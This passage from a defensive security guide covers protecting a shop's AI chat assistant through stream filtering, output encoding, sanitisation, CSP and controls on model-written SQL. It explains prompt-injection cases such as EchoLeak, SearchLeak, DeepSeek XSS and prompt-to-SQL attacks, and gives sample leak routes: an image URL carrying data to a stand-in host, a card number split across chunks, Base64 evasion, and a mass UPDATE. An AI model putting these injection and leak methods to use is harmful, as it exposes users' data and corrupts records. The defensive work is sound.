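A filter can instead check the response in chunks, holding each one until it passes. Microsoft's *Content streaming* describes this as the default mode, as does AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content*, which calls it "synchronous". If a later chunk fails, the stream stops, but the earlier chunks stay on the customer's screen unless the application removes them.

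Both companies also offer an asynchronous mode, which sends text immediately and checks it in the background. Microsoft guarantees a signal within about 1,000 characters of the offending text, and the application then has to remove text the customer can already see. AWS cannot mask personal data in this mode. Microsoft recommends asynchronous mode for uses such as internal development tools, and the default mode for customer-facing chatbots in regulated industries.

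Suppose a 300-word reply (1,800 characters) opens with dangerous advice. The model writes 30 words a second, the customer reads four words a second, and each check takes 0.3 seconds.

| Method | Wait before any checked text could appear | Words sent before the block | Words the customer has time to read |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hold the whole reply | 10.3 s | 0 | 0 |
| Hold chunks of 300 characters | 2.0 s | 0 | 0 |
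| Send first, with a signal after 1,000 characters | None | About 167 | About 22 |

Twenty-two words are enough to cause harm, since "Yes, that's fine in a closed room" is only seven. A slower model makes this worse because the customer has time to read more. At ten words a second, the 1,000 characters take almost 17 seconds to arrive, and the customer can read about 67 words in that time.

Cisco documents a gateway that combines these methods. In its blocking mode, it holds the first 1,024 bytes of text, then scans again whenever the text has grown by at least 500 characters. These scans use only text patterns, because a language model would be too slow to judge every chunk. The gateway runs the full check once the reply is complete, so the customer may already have seen politely worded bad advice that matches no pattern. It does hold each tool call until that call passes its check, which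 is sensible because an application can't retract a refund.

Some products don't filter streams at all, or do so only in certain configurations. Cloudflare's AI Gateway is a separate product that does check responses. According to Cloudflare's *Usage considerations*, the gateway holds the full reply before returning it on one set of addresses. On the other, it checks the streamed reply and logs the verdict, but the customer receives everything regardless. Google Cloud's *Model Armor release notes* list streaming for text as a preview feature from May 12, 2026. When Model Armor runs on Google's agent gateway, streaming is limited to agents built with the company's own development kit, according to Google Cloud's *Integrate Model Armor with Agent Gateway*.

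### A card number split across two chunks

Chunks can also hide data that a filter would find in the full text. AWS's *StreamingConfigurations* gives 50 characters as the default interval between guardrail checks on an agent's stream. Cutting the earlier sentence from the staff report at that length splits the card number:

```text
Chunk 1:  Maria Lopez paid for order 482915307 with card 411
Chunk 2:  1 1111 1111 1111.
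```

A filter that checks each chunk separately finds three digits in the first and 13 in the second. Thirteen digits are enough for a card number, but these fail the Luhn check with a total of 19, so a detector that relies on that check ignores them. Both chunks pass the filter, and the customer's screen shows all 16 digits together.

The remedy is to overlap the chunks. A card number has at most 19 digits, or 23 characters with spaces between groups of four. If the filter holds back the last 22 characters of each chunk and checks them with the next, it always checks the complete number before any digit goes out. If it rechecked those characters without holding them back, as many as 15 digits of a 16-digit number could already be on the screen when it found the number.

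Postal addresses need a longer overlap between chunks, and judging whether advice is dangerous may require the whole reply so far. The shop could filter the live chat in overlapping chunks, holding each one until it has been checked, and hold the full text of emails, exports and tool calls, where nobody is watching the words appear.

### When the check cannot run

When a filter can't run its check, it fails open if it lets the text through and fails closed if it withholds the text. One product can do both. Zuplo's *Akamai AI Firewall Policy* describes a plug-in for Zuplo's AI gateway. The plug-in blocks by default when Akamai's service is unavailable, but it passes a reply whose JSON it can't parse.

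| What goes wrong | What happens by default | What the caller or the log shows |
|---|---|---|
| Zuplo: Akamai is down, limits the number of calls or rejects the key | Blocked | Status 502, with the code `guardrail_unavailable` |
| Zuplo: the plug-in doesn't know the request's format | Blocked | Status 400, with the code `guardrail_uninspectable` |
| Zuplo: the JSON of a successful reply doesn't parse | Passed unchecked | No documented error code |
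| Zuplo: a late chunk fails the check | Stream stops | The original success status, then a content-filter stop |
| Cloudflare's AI Gateway: the classifier doesn't answer | Blocked if any category is set to "block"; passed if set only to "flag" | No documented error code |

The most worrying row is the unparseable reply, because it can look like a normal success. An attacker probably can't cause it just by steering the model's words, since the model provider wraps those words in JSON and escapes the special characters. But it could result from a fault at the provider, a connection that drops partway through the reply, or a custom model server that writes invalid JSON. An application can avoid the problem by refusing any reply it can't parse.

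Operators also need to decide what happens when a check times out. Radwan and Deschamps write that Cloudflare's firewall limits each analysis to two seconds, then uses whichever detections have finished. A request could therefore go ahead with a PII verdict but no verdict on unsafe topics. In October 2026 Cloudflare added a field that lists failed detections, but it has no effect unless the customer writes a rule to block or log those requests.

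Very long text can cause the same trouble. Cloudflare's AI Gateway splits it into smaller pieces and checks each one, which takes longer than the usual half second. If a product has a size limit, the shop should find out whether text beyond that limit gets through unchecked, and keep its replies shorter than the limit.

For customer chat, failing closed is usually right, because the customer gets a preset message and can ask for a person. A rule that only counts swear words can fail open. Zuplo warns that with a filter that fails open, an expired key can leave the gateway returning successful responses without inspection, and suggests monitoring for a sudden drop in blocks.

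Logs can be misleading even when the filter works. AWS reports the same stop reason, `guardrail_intervened`, whether the guardrail blocked a reply or only masked a name in it, so a dashboard that counts this value will overcount blocks. The detailed trace shows whether the reply was blocked or masked, but it also contains the unmasked name and the original reply, so the shop has to protect it like the customer database. Microsoft's service returns status 200, the code for success, when the filter cuts off a reply, so an alarm that checks only for error codes will miss it. Zuplo's older plug-in has a setting that lets a response through after an Akamai alert without writing a log line.

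AWS's trace also records how many characters the guardrail checked. In AWS's example, it checked 39 of 72, and the other 33 match the length of a sentence that the developer hadn't marked. The shop can raise an alarm whenever the number checked differs unexpectedly from the total. For any product, it can compare the number of replies sent with the number of verdicts received. If the application sent a million replies and received 990,000 verdicts, 10,000 replies reached customers unchecked.

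### The order of filtering and encoding

Output encoding protects a page only if nothing changes the text afterwards. Suppose the shop uses reversible tokens, and customer 17 has registered the awkward surname from the earlier example. The order of two steps decides whether the browser treats the tags as tags:

```text
Model's reply:          Thank you, NAME_17.
Encode, then restore:   Thank you, O'<b>MARKER</b>.
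Restore, then encode:   Thank you, O&#39;&lt;b&gt;MARKER&lt;/b&gt;.
```

In the second line, the application encoded a harmless token and then inserted live HTML. In the third, the customer sees the surname exactly as typed.

A developer can do the same damage while fixing a display bug. If two parts of the application both encode the text, customers see `O&#39;Brien` on the page. The developer might decode the text at the end, which restores the apostrophe but also any HTML tags. The safe fix is to remove the extra encoding step.

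A PII filter should run on plain characters, before the text is encoded, because a filter that searches for O'Brien may not match `O&#39;Brien`. If the application decodes text after the check, the filter has checked something different from what the customer will read.

Masking can break structured data too. Replacing the digits in `{"order": 482915307}` with asterisks leaves invalid JSON, which the next program may reject or, as in Zuplo's case, pass along unchecked. The application should parse the data, mask the values, and convert the result back to JSON.

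For the chat page, a workable order is to decode the reply once, run the content filter and apply its masks, restore the tokens this customer may see, and encode for the page last. Other sinks need the same order with their own final step. A filter at the network edge may receive a page that the application has already encoded. It can safely block the page or log a match, but if it decodes the page to mask a name, it has to encode the text again before sending it on.

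## Showing model output safely in a browser

A web page reaches the browser as a string of characters, which the browser reads in order. A left angle bracket followed by a letter normally opens a tag, which can set the layout, load an image or run a script. Most other characters are text to display. The string doesn't record who wrote each part, so on a shop's website, a tag in a stranger's review works just like one written by the shop's developers.

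Cross-site scripting (XSS) is dangerous because the browser treats a script inside the shop's page as the shop's own. Browsers normally stop a script on one site from reading another site's pages or saved data, but a script in the shop's page can read the customer's order details, send requests under the customer's login, and sometimes copy the session token, a string that identifies the signed-in user. Anyone who has that token can usually use the account without a password.

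On a chat page, the shop's own script adds each reply to a page that is already open. Auth0's *Trusting AI Output?*, a guide from a company that sells login software, contrasts two ways to do this:

```js
message.textContent = "<b>MARKER</b>";  // the customer sees the tags as typed
message.innerHTML = "<b>MARKER</b>";    // the customer sees MARKER in bold
```

The first line inserts the reply as text, which has the same effect as HTML encoding. The second makes the browser interpret the reply as HTML. Auth0's example of an attack on the second line uses a script tag, which current browsers don't run when a page inserts it this way. The advice is still sound because several other tags can run scripts, and a filter that looks only for script tags would miss them.

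### Why Markdown reopens the question

Chat models usually format their replies in Markdown, in which two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold. The chat page converts `**MARKER**` to `<strong>MARKER</strong>` and then has to insert the result as HTML. If it used the safer method and inserted the whole reply as text, the customer would see the tags.

Markdown's original design lets authors mix HTML tags into their text, and some converters still pass those tags through unless a developer turns the feature off. Even with HTML turned off, a reply can make the browser contact another company's server, because Markdown has its own syntax for links and images.

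### Output shown at once and output saved for later

If the assistant's reply goes straight back to the person who asked, a customer who gets it to write a script attacks only their own browser. To reach someone else, an attacker needs indirect prompt injection, for example through a review or an uploaded document. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian classify attacks through an immediate reply as reflected XSS.

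In stored XSS, the application saves the model's output and later displays it to another person. This could happen with tickets, reports, comments, generated documents and chat histories. Suppose the shop's assistant passes a difficult complaint to staff by creating a ticket containing the conversation. The attacker only has to ask the assistant to repeat a malicious string, then wait for an employee to open the ticket. That employee can probably issue refunds and look up any customer.

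The live chat and the ticket page may run on different code, so a safe chat page doesn't show that the ticket page is safe. A review of the server's code can also miss the fault if a script in the browser inserts the reply, as in Auth0's example. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian call this form DOM-based, after the DOM, the browser's internal model of the page.

### DeepSeek's chat page

In late 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger asked DeepSeek's chatbot to list some well-known test strings for cross-site scripting (XSS). *DeepSeek AI*, a post on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, reports that the chat page ran one of them. Rehberger had typed an ordinary English sentence, so checking the user's message for HTML tags would have found nothing.

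Rehberger then showed how an attacker could attack another user. An uploaded text file contained instructions and encoded active markup. The model decoded the markup and wrote it into its reply. The page then ran the markup, which displayed the user's session token. The demonstration didn't send the token anywhere, but Rehberger says that would be easy to add. DeepSeek fixed the flaw a day after Rehberger's exchange with the company.

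A later report about DeepSeek is harder to judge. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-26210* (2025), an entry in the vulnerability database of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, rates the severity of scripts running on a separate DeepSeek domain at 8.8 out of 10, but notes that some people consider this behaviour intended. A product that previews web pages written by a model has to run their scripts somewhere, and a separate domain is sensible because the browser then stops those scripts from accessing the chat page's data. The risk depends on what else that domain can access, which the entry doesn't describe.

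### From a medical chatbot to an administrator's account

In 2026 Quarkslab, the company behind the raw-data attack on a support assistant, described another authorised attack, this time on a customer's live system. It reproduced the flaws in a mock medical chatbot to keep the customer anonymous.

The chat page displayed an image that the team had asked the model to include. The team then got the page to run a script, which could read the session cookie because the site hadn't set HttpOnly, a flag that hides a cookie from scripts. At this point the team could attack only its own account.

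Every conversation had a predictable web address, and the server didn't check whether the person opening it owned the conversation. The team could save the script in one of its own conversations and send someone else the link. If an administrator clicked it, the team could capture the administrator's session and take over the whole platform.

An ownership check would have closed that route and kept patients' conversations private. But administrators who review flagged conversations are allowed to open them, so the script would still have run when they did. Marking the cookie HttpOnly would have stopped the script from reading it, but the script could still have sent requests in the administrator's name. Quarkslab therefore mainly recommended validating and encoding every response from the model, with a stricter page policy and proper permission checks as further measures.

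### Leaking data through an image's address

A page can also leak data without running a script. Here is an ordinary Markdown image, with a marker where an attacker would want private data:

```text
![Your boots](https://images.example/boots.png?note=MARKER)
```

The browser sends the whole address when it requests the image, so whoever runs the server finds MARKER in its log, even if the customer sees only a broken image.

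EchoLeak, the best-known case of this kind, was a flaw that researchers at Aim Labs found in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can search an employee's email, files and chats (Ravia, 2025, *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*). The attacker only had to send the employee an email. When the employee later asked Copilot about a related subject, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal documents, followed the email's instructions, and wrote an image address containing the most sensitive information it had.

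Microsoft had three defences in the way, and each one failed:

- A classifier screened incoming text for prompt injection but didn't recognise the email. Ravia points out that such an email is hard to detect because its instructions could be meant for the human recipient.
- Copilot removed external links and images from its replies, but it recognised only the usual Markdown syntax. The page also converted a less common form, which the filter left in place.
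- The page allowed images only from listed hosts. One of them, a Microsoft Teams service, would fetch any address included in a request, so it passed the data on to the attacker's server.

The flaw was reported privately in January 2025, fixed in May and disclosed publicly on June 11, according to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025). Microsoft rated its severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft knew of no customer attacked through the flaw.

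### Why content filters miss the leak

A toxicity filter would pass such a reply, just as it would pass a polite one containing a script. A PII filter might recognise a street address inside the image's address, if it inspects that part of the reply at all, but the model can encode the data first. Base64, for example, is a common way to write data as letters, digits and a few symbols:

```text
Plain:     12 Mill Lane
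Base64:    MTIgTWlsbCBMYW5l
```

The second line doesn't look like an address, but anyone can convert it back. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026), an account of another Copilot flaw, notes that this encoding helps data get past filters that scan for passwords or keys. A filter could decode Base64 before checking, but the attacker can ask the model to use another encoding it knows or invent a simple one.

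Controlling where the browser sends requests is therefore more reliable. Microsoft (2025) calls such defences deterministic because they guarantee that a particular attack will fail. As EchoLeak shows, the guarantee applies only to the routes a defence covers.

### Step 1: encode by default

Every reply should start out as plain text, inserted with `textContent` or its equivalent. This stops scripts and images because the browser creates no HTML elements from the reply. If the shop's assistant writes only short answers, it may not need formatting, and the developers can tell the model to write without it. If the model uses Markdown anyway, the customer sees a few asterisks.

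Encoding fails wherever a developer bypasses it. Quarkslab's mock chatbot used React, a web page library that encodes text by default, but its page still inserted the model's HTML. Searching the code for `innerHTML` and similar features will find most of these bypasses, including those on the ticket page and in the export tool.

### Step 2: convert Markdown with raw HTML off, then sanitise

If the shop wants bold text and lists, it should use a converter with raw HTML turned off. The setting has this effect:

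```text
Reply:            **MARKER** <b>MARKER</b>
Raw HTML on:      <strong>MARKER</strong> <b>MARKER</b>
Raw HTML off:     <strong>MARKER</strong> &lt;b&gt;MARKER&lt;/b&gt;
```

With raw HTML off, the customer sees the first MARKER in bold and the second with its tags as typed. Encoding the whole reply before conversion, rather than turning raw HTML off, breaks Markdown's quotation marks and can make code samples display `&lt;` instead of an angle bracket. It also leaves Markdown's links and images working.

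The application should then pass the converted HTML through a sanitiser, which keeps only the tags and attributes on an allow-list. The shop might allow paragraphs, bold text, lists and links. The sanitiser has to run after the conversion because the converter creates new tags, and a bug or an add-on might create one the shop doesn't want.

A maintained library is a better way to sanitise HTML than a few home-made patterns. HTML has complicated rules for repairing badly formed tags, and if a sanitiser applies them differently from the browser, text that looked harmless can become active on the page. Maintainers fix these differences as researchers find them, so the shop also has to install the updates.

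A sanitiser's default settings may not be strict enough. DOMPurify, which is widely used, removes scripts but normally keeps images, so it wouldn't stop a leak like EchoLeak without further configuration. Code that changes the HTML after sanitising can also make it unsafe again, for example when an application replaces a token with a customer's surname.

Output also has to be made safe before the browser renders any of it. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a flaw in the enterprise search feature of Microsoft 365 Copilot. The victim clicked a link that led to Microsoft's own site and contained a prompt. Copilot then searched the victim's mailbox and wrote an image tag whose address contained an email's subject line. Microsoft's protection turned the reply into harmless text, but only after the model had finished writing. While the reply was still streaming, the page briefly rendered the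 raw HTML, and the browser requested the image.

Varonis advises sanitising output when the page displays it. For a streamed reply, the page can convert and sanitise all the text received so far each time a new chunk arrives, then replace what is on the screen. Sanitising each chunk separately could miss a tag split across two chunks.

### Step 3: allow only listed links and image hosts

A link begins with a scheme, such as `https:` for a web page or `mailto:` for an email. Some schemes are dangerous, including `javascript:`, which makes the browser run the rest of the link as a script when someone clicks it. N45HT's *Hacking AI with Markdown* reports a flaw of this kind in DeepSeek's chat, and DeepSeek changed its Markdown processing to prevent this. The shop can allow only `https:` and perhaps `mailto:`.

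The code should check addresses in the converted HTML, because conversion turns every Markdown variant into the same kind of tag. This avoids the mistake in Copilot's link filter. The code should also parse each address and compare the exact host. A rule that only searches for `shop.example` would accept `https://shop.example.files.example/`, which belongs to the owner of `files.example`.

An `https:` link can still carry private data. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes a Microsoft 365 Copilot flaw in which a phishing email led the assistant to search the user's inbox and put what it found into a link, in characters the user couldn't see. Clicking the link would have sent the data to the attacker. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024, and Amazon dealt with a leak in its assistant Q for Business by no longer displaying links. The shop could allow links only to its own help pages, so that any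 data in a link would go to the shop's server.

The simplest rule for images is to refuse external ones. According to the security company Checkmarx, Google's Gemini does this with its sanitiser, while Microsoft didn't commit to fixing a leak through images in Copilot Chat because it didn't consider the leak a vulnerability.

The shop can still show pictures of its boots by having the model write a product number. The application checks that the product exists and inserts the picture's address from the catalogue. The model chooses which picture to show but never writes an address, much as it supplies a value to a parameterised query without writing the query.

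If the model does have to write image addresses, the shop needs a list of permitted hosts, and it has to know what each host does with a request. In these four cases the list worked as designed, but the data still got out:

| Case | Permitted host | How the data got out |
|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, Microsoft 365 Copilot (2025) | Microsoft Teams | A Teams service fetched the attacker's address |
| ForcedLeak, Salesforce Agentforce (2025) | A domain that Salesforce had let expire | Researchers registered the domain and read its logs |
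| Superhuman, an email application (January 2026) | Google Docs | The image request submitted a form that the attacker owned |
| SearchLeak, Microsoft 365 Copilot (June 2026) | Bing | The image search fetched the attacker's address |

The list of hosts Ravia published in 2025 already included Bing, so closing the route through Teams left the one through Bing open, and researchers found it a year later.

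Willison, a programmer who collects cases like these, reports that Salesforce corrected its list of allowed hosts after ForcedLeak and began restricting the links its agents can produce. Developers need to keep reviewing such a list, because a host that was safe when they added it can change hands later.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack that, in one test, leaked parts of more than 40 emails through a single reply. When a user asked Superhuman to summarize recent mail, hidden instructions in one message made the assistant put the contents of other emails into an image address that submitted a Google form. PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of AI suppliers, reported the flaw on a Friday in December 2025, and Superhuman disabled the affected features the following Monday.

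PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes the same use of a Google form to extract emails from OpenAI's Codex. PromptArmor reported the flaw in April 2026, and OpenAI has since fixed it.

The shop's own servers can have this weakness too. Many sites have a service that resizes pictures, and some of these accept the address of a picture on another site. If the shop's service does, an image request to the shop can carry data to an attacker. PromptArmor advised Notion, which makes note-taking software, to make sure that the image server can't redirect requests elsewhere. The shop's resizing service should accept only the names of files it already stores.

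### Step 4: set a Content Security Policy

A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a set of rules that a server sends with a page. It tells the browser which scripts may run and where the page may load images and other material from. OWASP recommends a strict one for pages that display model output. A starting point for the shop's chat page might be:

```text
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
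  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  connect-src 'self';
  img-src 'self';
  form-action 'self';
  base-uri 'none'
```

The first rule blocks everything the later ones don't allow. `'self'` means the page's own site, so the browser can load the shop's script files, styles and pictures but not an image from another site. The browser also blocks scripts written directly into the page, as a script in a model's reply would be. The last two rules stop forms from sending data to other sites and stop a tag from changing where the page's relative links lead.

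The browser enforces these rules even if the sanitiser misses something. Such a policy would have stopped the script in Quarkslab's medical chatbot from running. Reddy and Gujral recommend a similar policy that blocks all scripts in the area that displays model output, though they worked from published accounts of EchoLeak and didn't test their defences.

A CSP can fail in several ways. Developers often add `'unsafe-inline'` to `script-src` to get an old feature working, which again allows scripts written into the page. If customers can upload files to the same site, an attacker may be able to upload a script that the browser treats as the shop's own. A broad list of image hosts has the weaknesses already described, and a CSP doesn't stop a customer from following a link that contains private data. The first three steps are therefore still necessary.

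The shop can first run the policy in report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations without blocking anything, to see which legitimate features would break. Once the shop enforces the policy, a report of a blocked outside image also means that the sanitiser has let something through.

### Messages that leave the page

A CSP protects only the page it comes with. If the shop's assistant also posts alerts to a staff Slack channel, a web address in an alert can leak data before anyone clicks it. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* explains that Slack fetches the linked page to show a preview, and that request contains the full address. The request comes from Slack's server, so nothing in the shop's page can block it.

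On Slack, the remedy is to set both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false in each message the application posts (Willison, 2024). Other messaging services have their own defaults. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can use through chat, was exposed by default on Telegram.

Emails that contain external images can leak data in the same way. In May 2026, Willison described a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which could send messages to the user's inbox without approval. An attacker's instructions could make it include an image whose address contained a download link for one of the user's files, and the link went to the attacker when the user opened the message. A shop that emails chat transcripts or reports should send them as plain text or remove every external image first.

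## Running database queries that a model wrote

A chat page can show almost any reply safely by treating it as text, but a database has to run a query to answer it. How well the shop can protect its orders therefore depends mainly on how much of each query the model writes.

### Values and whole queries

In the safer design, a developer writes the query and the model supplies only values. When a customer asks about the boots, the model passes on an order number and the application runs this:

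```sql
SELECT status, shipped_on FROM orders
WHERE order_id = ? AND customer_id = ?
```

This parameterised query takes the order number from the model and the customer's number from the login session. Using parameters fully prevents SQL injection here, but a developer still has to remember to include the condition on the customer's number, which is a permission check.

A placeholder can stand only for a value, so it can't supply a column's name, which is part of the command. If customers can sort their orders by date or price, the model should choose "date" or "price", and the application should look up the matching column in its own list.

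In the other design, called text-to-SQL, the model receives a question and a description of the database's tables, then writes the whole query. This suits questions that nobody planned for, such as which boots customers return most often in wet months. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025) points out that fixed queries require developers to predict all the data that future tasks will need.

OWASP's general advice to parameterise queries works for the first design but doesn't make text-to-SQL safe. In one OWASP scenario, a user asks a chat feature to delete every table. The resulting commands contain table names but no values, so there is nothing to parameterise.

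The standard definition of SQL injection, reproduced in the *CWE-89* entry of GCVE's public vulnerability database, concerns special characters that could modify the "intended" command. A text-to-SQL application has no intended command to compare with the model's. Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues (2025) found in *Prompt-to-SQL Injections in LLM-Integrated Web Applications* that, for much the same reason, conventional SQL sanitisation tools can't flag a harmful query that a model wrote from scratch. They recommend replacing model-written SQL with parameterised queries or APIs. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey, lists parameterised queries alongside read-only execution and output validation, but only the last two limit a query whose structure came from the model.

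### A customer asks for "my orders"

Suppose the shop uses text-to-SQL in its customer chat, and customer 17 types "Show me my orders". The model should write the first of these queries but writes the second:

```sql
SELECT order_id, status FROM orders WHERE customer_id = 17;
SELECT order_id, status FROM orders;
```

The second query is valid and reads only the table it needs, but it returns every order in the shop. This can happen without an attack, because the model may leave out the condition.

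A toxicity filter would pass the reply, because a list of order numbers and delivery statuses contains nothing toxic. A PII filter would probably pass it too, unless it misclassified the order numbers as driver's licence numbers. If the customer had asked how many orders they had placed, the same mistake would have produced a single number containing no personal data.

A query that changes data leaves even less to inspect. Here the customer has asked to cancel one order, and the model has again forgotten the condition:

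```sql
UPDATE orders SET status = 'cancelled';
```

The database cancels every order and returns only a count of the rows it changed. The assistant then writes "Your order has been cancelled", which any content filter would pass, but all the orders have already been cancelled. The row count is the only useful warning, and an application that expects to change one order can undo the transaction if the count is anything else.

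### The prompt-to-SQL study

Pedro, Carreira and colleagues in Lisbon introduced the term "prompt-to-SQL injection" for attacks that make a model write harmful queries, in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (2023). They built a job-listing site with a chatbot that used GPT-3.5 and LangChain, a popular library for connecting models to other software. The chatbot's account could read and change everything in the database.

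With LangChain's standard instructions, the chatbot deleted a table, changed a user's phone number and listed all users' details whenever someone asked. The team then added instructions that banned changes to data and limited each user to their own records. These stopped some simple attempts, such as when user 1 asked for user 2's email address. The model wrote a query for rows that belonged to both users at once, and the database returned nothing. But other requests got past each restriction in all 30 trials.

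An attacker could also reach the database without using the chatbot. The site let people post jobs, so the team planted instructions in a job description, which the chatbot read when another user asked about vacancies. One planted text made the chatbot answer that there were no jobs. It worked every time when the chatbot could run only one query per question, and 60% of the time when it could run several. Another text made the chatbot that could run several queries change a victim's email address and then answer the user's question normally. An output filter would have received only an ordinary answer about jobs, while the attacker could take over the victim's account through password recovery.

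The team tried seven models, five of which could run both versions reliably: GPT-3.5, GPT-4, PaLM 2, Llama 2 and Vicuna. The direct attacks and the planted false answer worked on all five. GPT-4 resisted the email attack in the 2023 study but not in the 2025 version. PaLM 2 and Llama 2 changed the address, then either revealed this in the answer or kept repeating the change.

The 2023 study also added a chatbot to an existing bookshop application and reproduced all the attacks there, with the planted instructions in product reviews. For the 2025 version, two outside security analysts spent up to three hours each on five open-source applications, and at least one attack worked on every application. Only the planted false answer worked on Dataherald, which held up best because its code refuses any query that changes data.

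The team built and timed several defences:

| Defence | What it stopped | Added delay |
|---|---|---|
| Database account that can only read (2023) | Changes to data | Negligible |
| Check that allows only SELECT queries (2025) | Changes to data | 0.7 ms |
| Loading the user's own data into the prompt beforehand (2023) | Direct requests for other users' data | 0.7 ms |
| Rewriting each query to cover only the user's rows (both) | Direct requests for other users' data | 1.87 ms |
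| Second model that screens query results (both) | Planted instructions | About 0.4 s |

In 2023 the second model added between 8% and 20% to the chatbot's response time. The 2025 version caught 99.55% of 1,120 malicious texts, missing about five, and flagged none of 150 harmless results. The malicious texts came from attacks on applications without such a guard, and from variations on those attacks. An attacker who knew about the guard might therefore do better, and Pedro and colleagues accept that targeted attacks could get round it.

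Loading the user's data beforehand gives weaker protection than the table suggests. It makes querying the database unnecessary, but a model that still has database access can query it anyway.

### Newer models and tools

The models in the Lisbon study are now several generations old, but the weakness has since appeared in widely used software. A follow-up article, *Words Become SQL* (Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues, 2025), lists three published vulnerabilities in libraries that connect models to databases. It also mentions cases in which attackers could bypass tools that were supposed to be read-only. Public reports of someone wiping a company's database this way are still rare. The article attributes this to limited disclosure and the novelty of these systems, but it could also mean that few attackers have tried.

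*OMNI-LEAK* (2026) tested database agents built on more recent models, including OpenAI's o4-mini, and found no consistent link between a database's size and the number of attempts an attacker needed, so a large company can't rely on the size of its database to hide sensitive rows. Only one category of attack worked on o4-mini, but the model's accuracy on ordinary questions while under attack fell from 90% with the smallest database to 76% with the largest.

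Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Data Agents Under Attack*, tried 14 attack techniques on six systems, including the commercial products Databricks Genie and Google's BigQuery, and found substantial vulnerabilities. One risk they describe is a series of permitted queries that together reveal a secret. For example, a shop employee who is allowed to see only totals could ask how much customers in a small town spent, then ask again excluding those who wear size 15. If the harbour pilot is the only customer there who wears that size, the difference between the two totals is the pilot's spending.

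In tests of agents in general, planted instructions succeed at very different rates. In a public competition with 464 participants, *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) recorded success rates from 0.5% to 8.5% across 13 models, even though an attack counted only if it also stayed hidden from the user. *INFUSE* (2026) found that attacks compromised 19.6% of runs on average. They compromised 26.3% of runs with GPT-5 but 8.4% with the much smaller GPT-5-Nano, so a more capable model isn't necessarily safer.

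Some of the variation in success rates comes from how attacks are scored. *Silent Failures in Agentic Security Evaluation* (2026) rescored identical runs and got a success rate of 21.7% when it counted any use of the tool the attacker wanted, but 1.2% when it also checked the arguments. For a database agent, the first method would count every query, while the second would count only harmful ones. Even at a 0.5% success rate, a planted review would succeed about five times in 1,000 independent attempts.

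The shop can't rely on the model to respect permissions either. According to *Role-Conditioned Refusals* (2025), text-to-SQL models focus on writing correct queries and leave access control to the database. *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (2026) requires a query to return the right result and use only what the user's role allows, but its permissions cover tables, columns and operations, not rows. The query that returned every customer's orders could comply with those permissions and fail only because its result was wrong.

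### Controls, from strongest to weakest

Fixed query templates are the strongest control because the model doesn't write any of the query's structure. Limits that the database enforces are the next strongest, since they apply however the model words a query. Checks in the application's code are weaker because they work only if they interpret each query correctly. These controls stop different mistakes, so an application that needs text-to-SQL should combine several.

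With **fixed query templates**, the model picks a template such as "order status" or "recent orders" and supplies the values, and the application adds the customer's number. The model can't leave out the condition that limits the query to that customer, because it doesn't write the query. It can still pick the wrong template or order, and a developer can forget the condition, but the shop can test each template once and reuse it. A dozen or so templates would probably cover nearly everything customers ask about their orders, so the customer chat has little need for text-to-SQL, which is easier to justify for the managers' reports.

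**Restricted views.** A view is a saved query that behaves like a table:

```sql
CREATE VIEW report_orders AS
SELECT order_id, product, status, ordered_on, returned_on
FROM orders;
```

If the reporting account can read this view but not the orders table, it cannot retrieve names, addresses or fraud scores, whatever query the model writes. It can still read every row in the view, and some combinations of details may identify a customer.

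The application runs the model's queries through **a read-only account** on a separate connection. Cancellations and refunds, which change data, go through services that developers wrote. The account doesn't limit which rows the model can read, so the mistaken query for "my orders" would still return every order. Some databases also let a SELECT query call stored functions that change data, so the shop has to revoke the account's permission to run them.

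**Row-level security.** The database adds a condition of its own to every query on a table. In PostgreSQL, which the Lisbon study used, the shop could write:

```sql
ALTER TABLE orders ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
CREATE POLICY own_orders ON orders FOR SELECT
  USING (customer_id = current_setting('shop.customer_id')::int);
```

The application sets `shop.customer_id` from the login session before it runs the model's query. The query without a customer condition then returns only customer 17's orders.

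This setup can fail in several ways. PostgreSQL normally exempts a table's owner from the policy, so the model's queries need to run under a different account. A view usually reads tables with its owner's rights, so it can bypass the policy too. PostgreSQL also lets an ordinary account change a custom setting like this one, so a model's query could switch to another customer unless the application blocks the commands and functions that change the setting. If a product connects every user through one shared account without passing on who is signed in, the database can't apply the right policy. Wang and colleagues warn that such accounts often have broader rights than the person asking.

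**Parsing the query.** A parser breaks the query into its grammatical parts, so the application can accept a single SELECT statement that uses only listed tables, columns and functions. It can also rewrite the query, as Pedro and colleagues do:

```sql
SELECT order_id, status
FROM (SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer_id = 17) AS own_orders;
```

The result is the same as with row-level security only if the parser finds every reference to the table, including those in views and functions. The parser also has to use the database's SQL dialect. In PostgreSQL, a statement that is mainly a SELECT can also delete rows, so the check has to cover the whole statement.

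**Limits on time and rows.** LangChain's standard prompt in the Lisbon study told the model to limit its results, but a model may not follow that instruction. The application should enforce the limits, for example by stopping a query after five seconds and reading at most 200 rows. The time limit matters because, as Wang and colleagues explain, a few unusual values planted in a column that links two tables can make a valid query need many times more computation. A row limit wouldn't help if the query did all that work to return one total. Running reports on a copy of the database also keeps a slow query from delaying customers' orders. Neither limit prevents a small leak, such as a single row containing a stranger's address.

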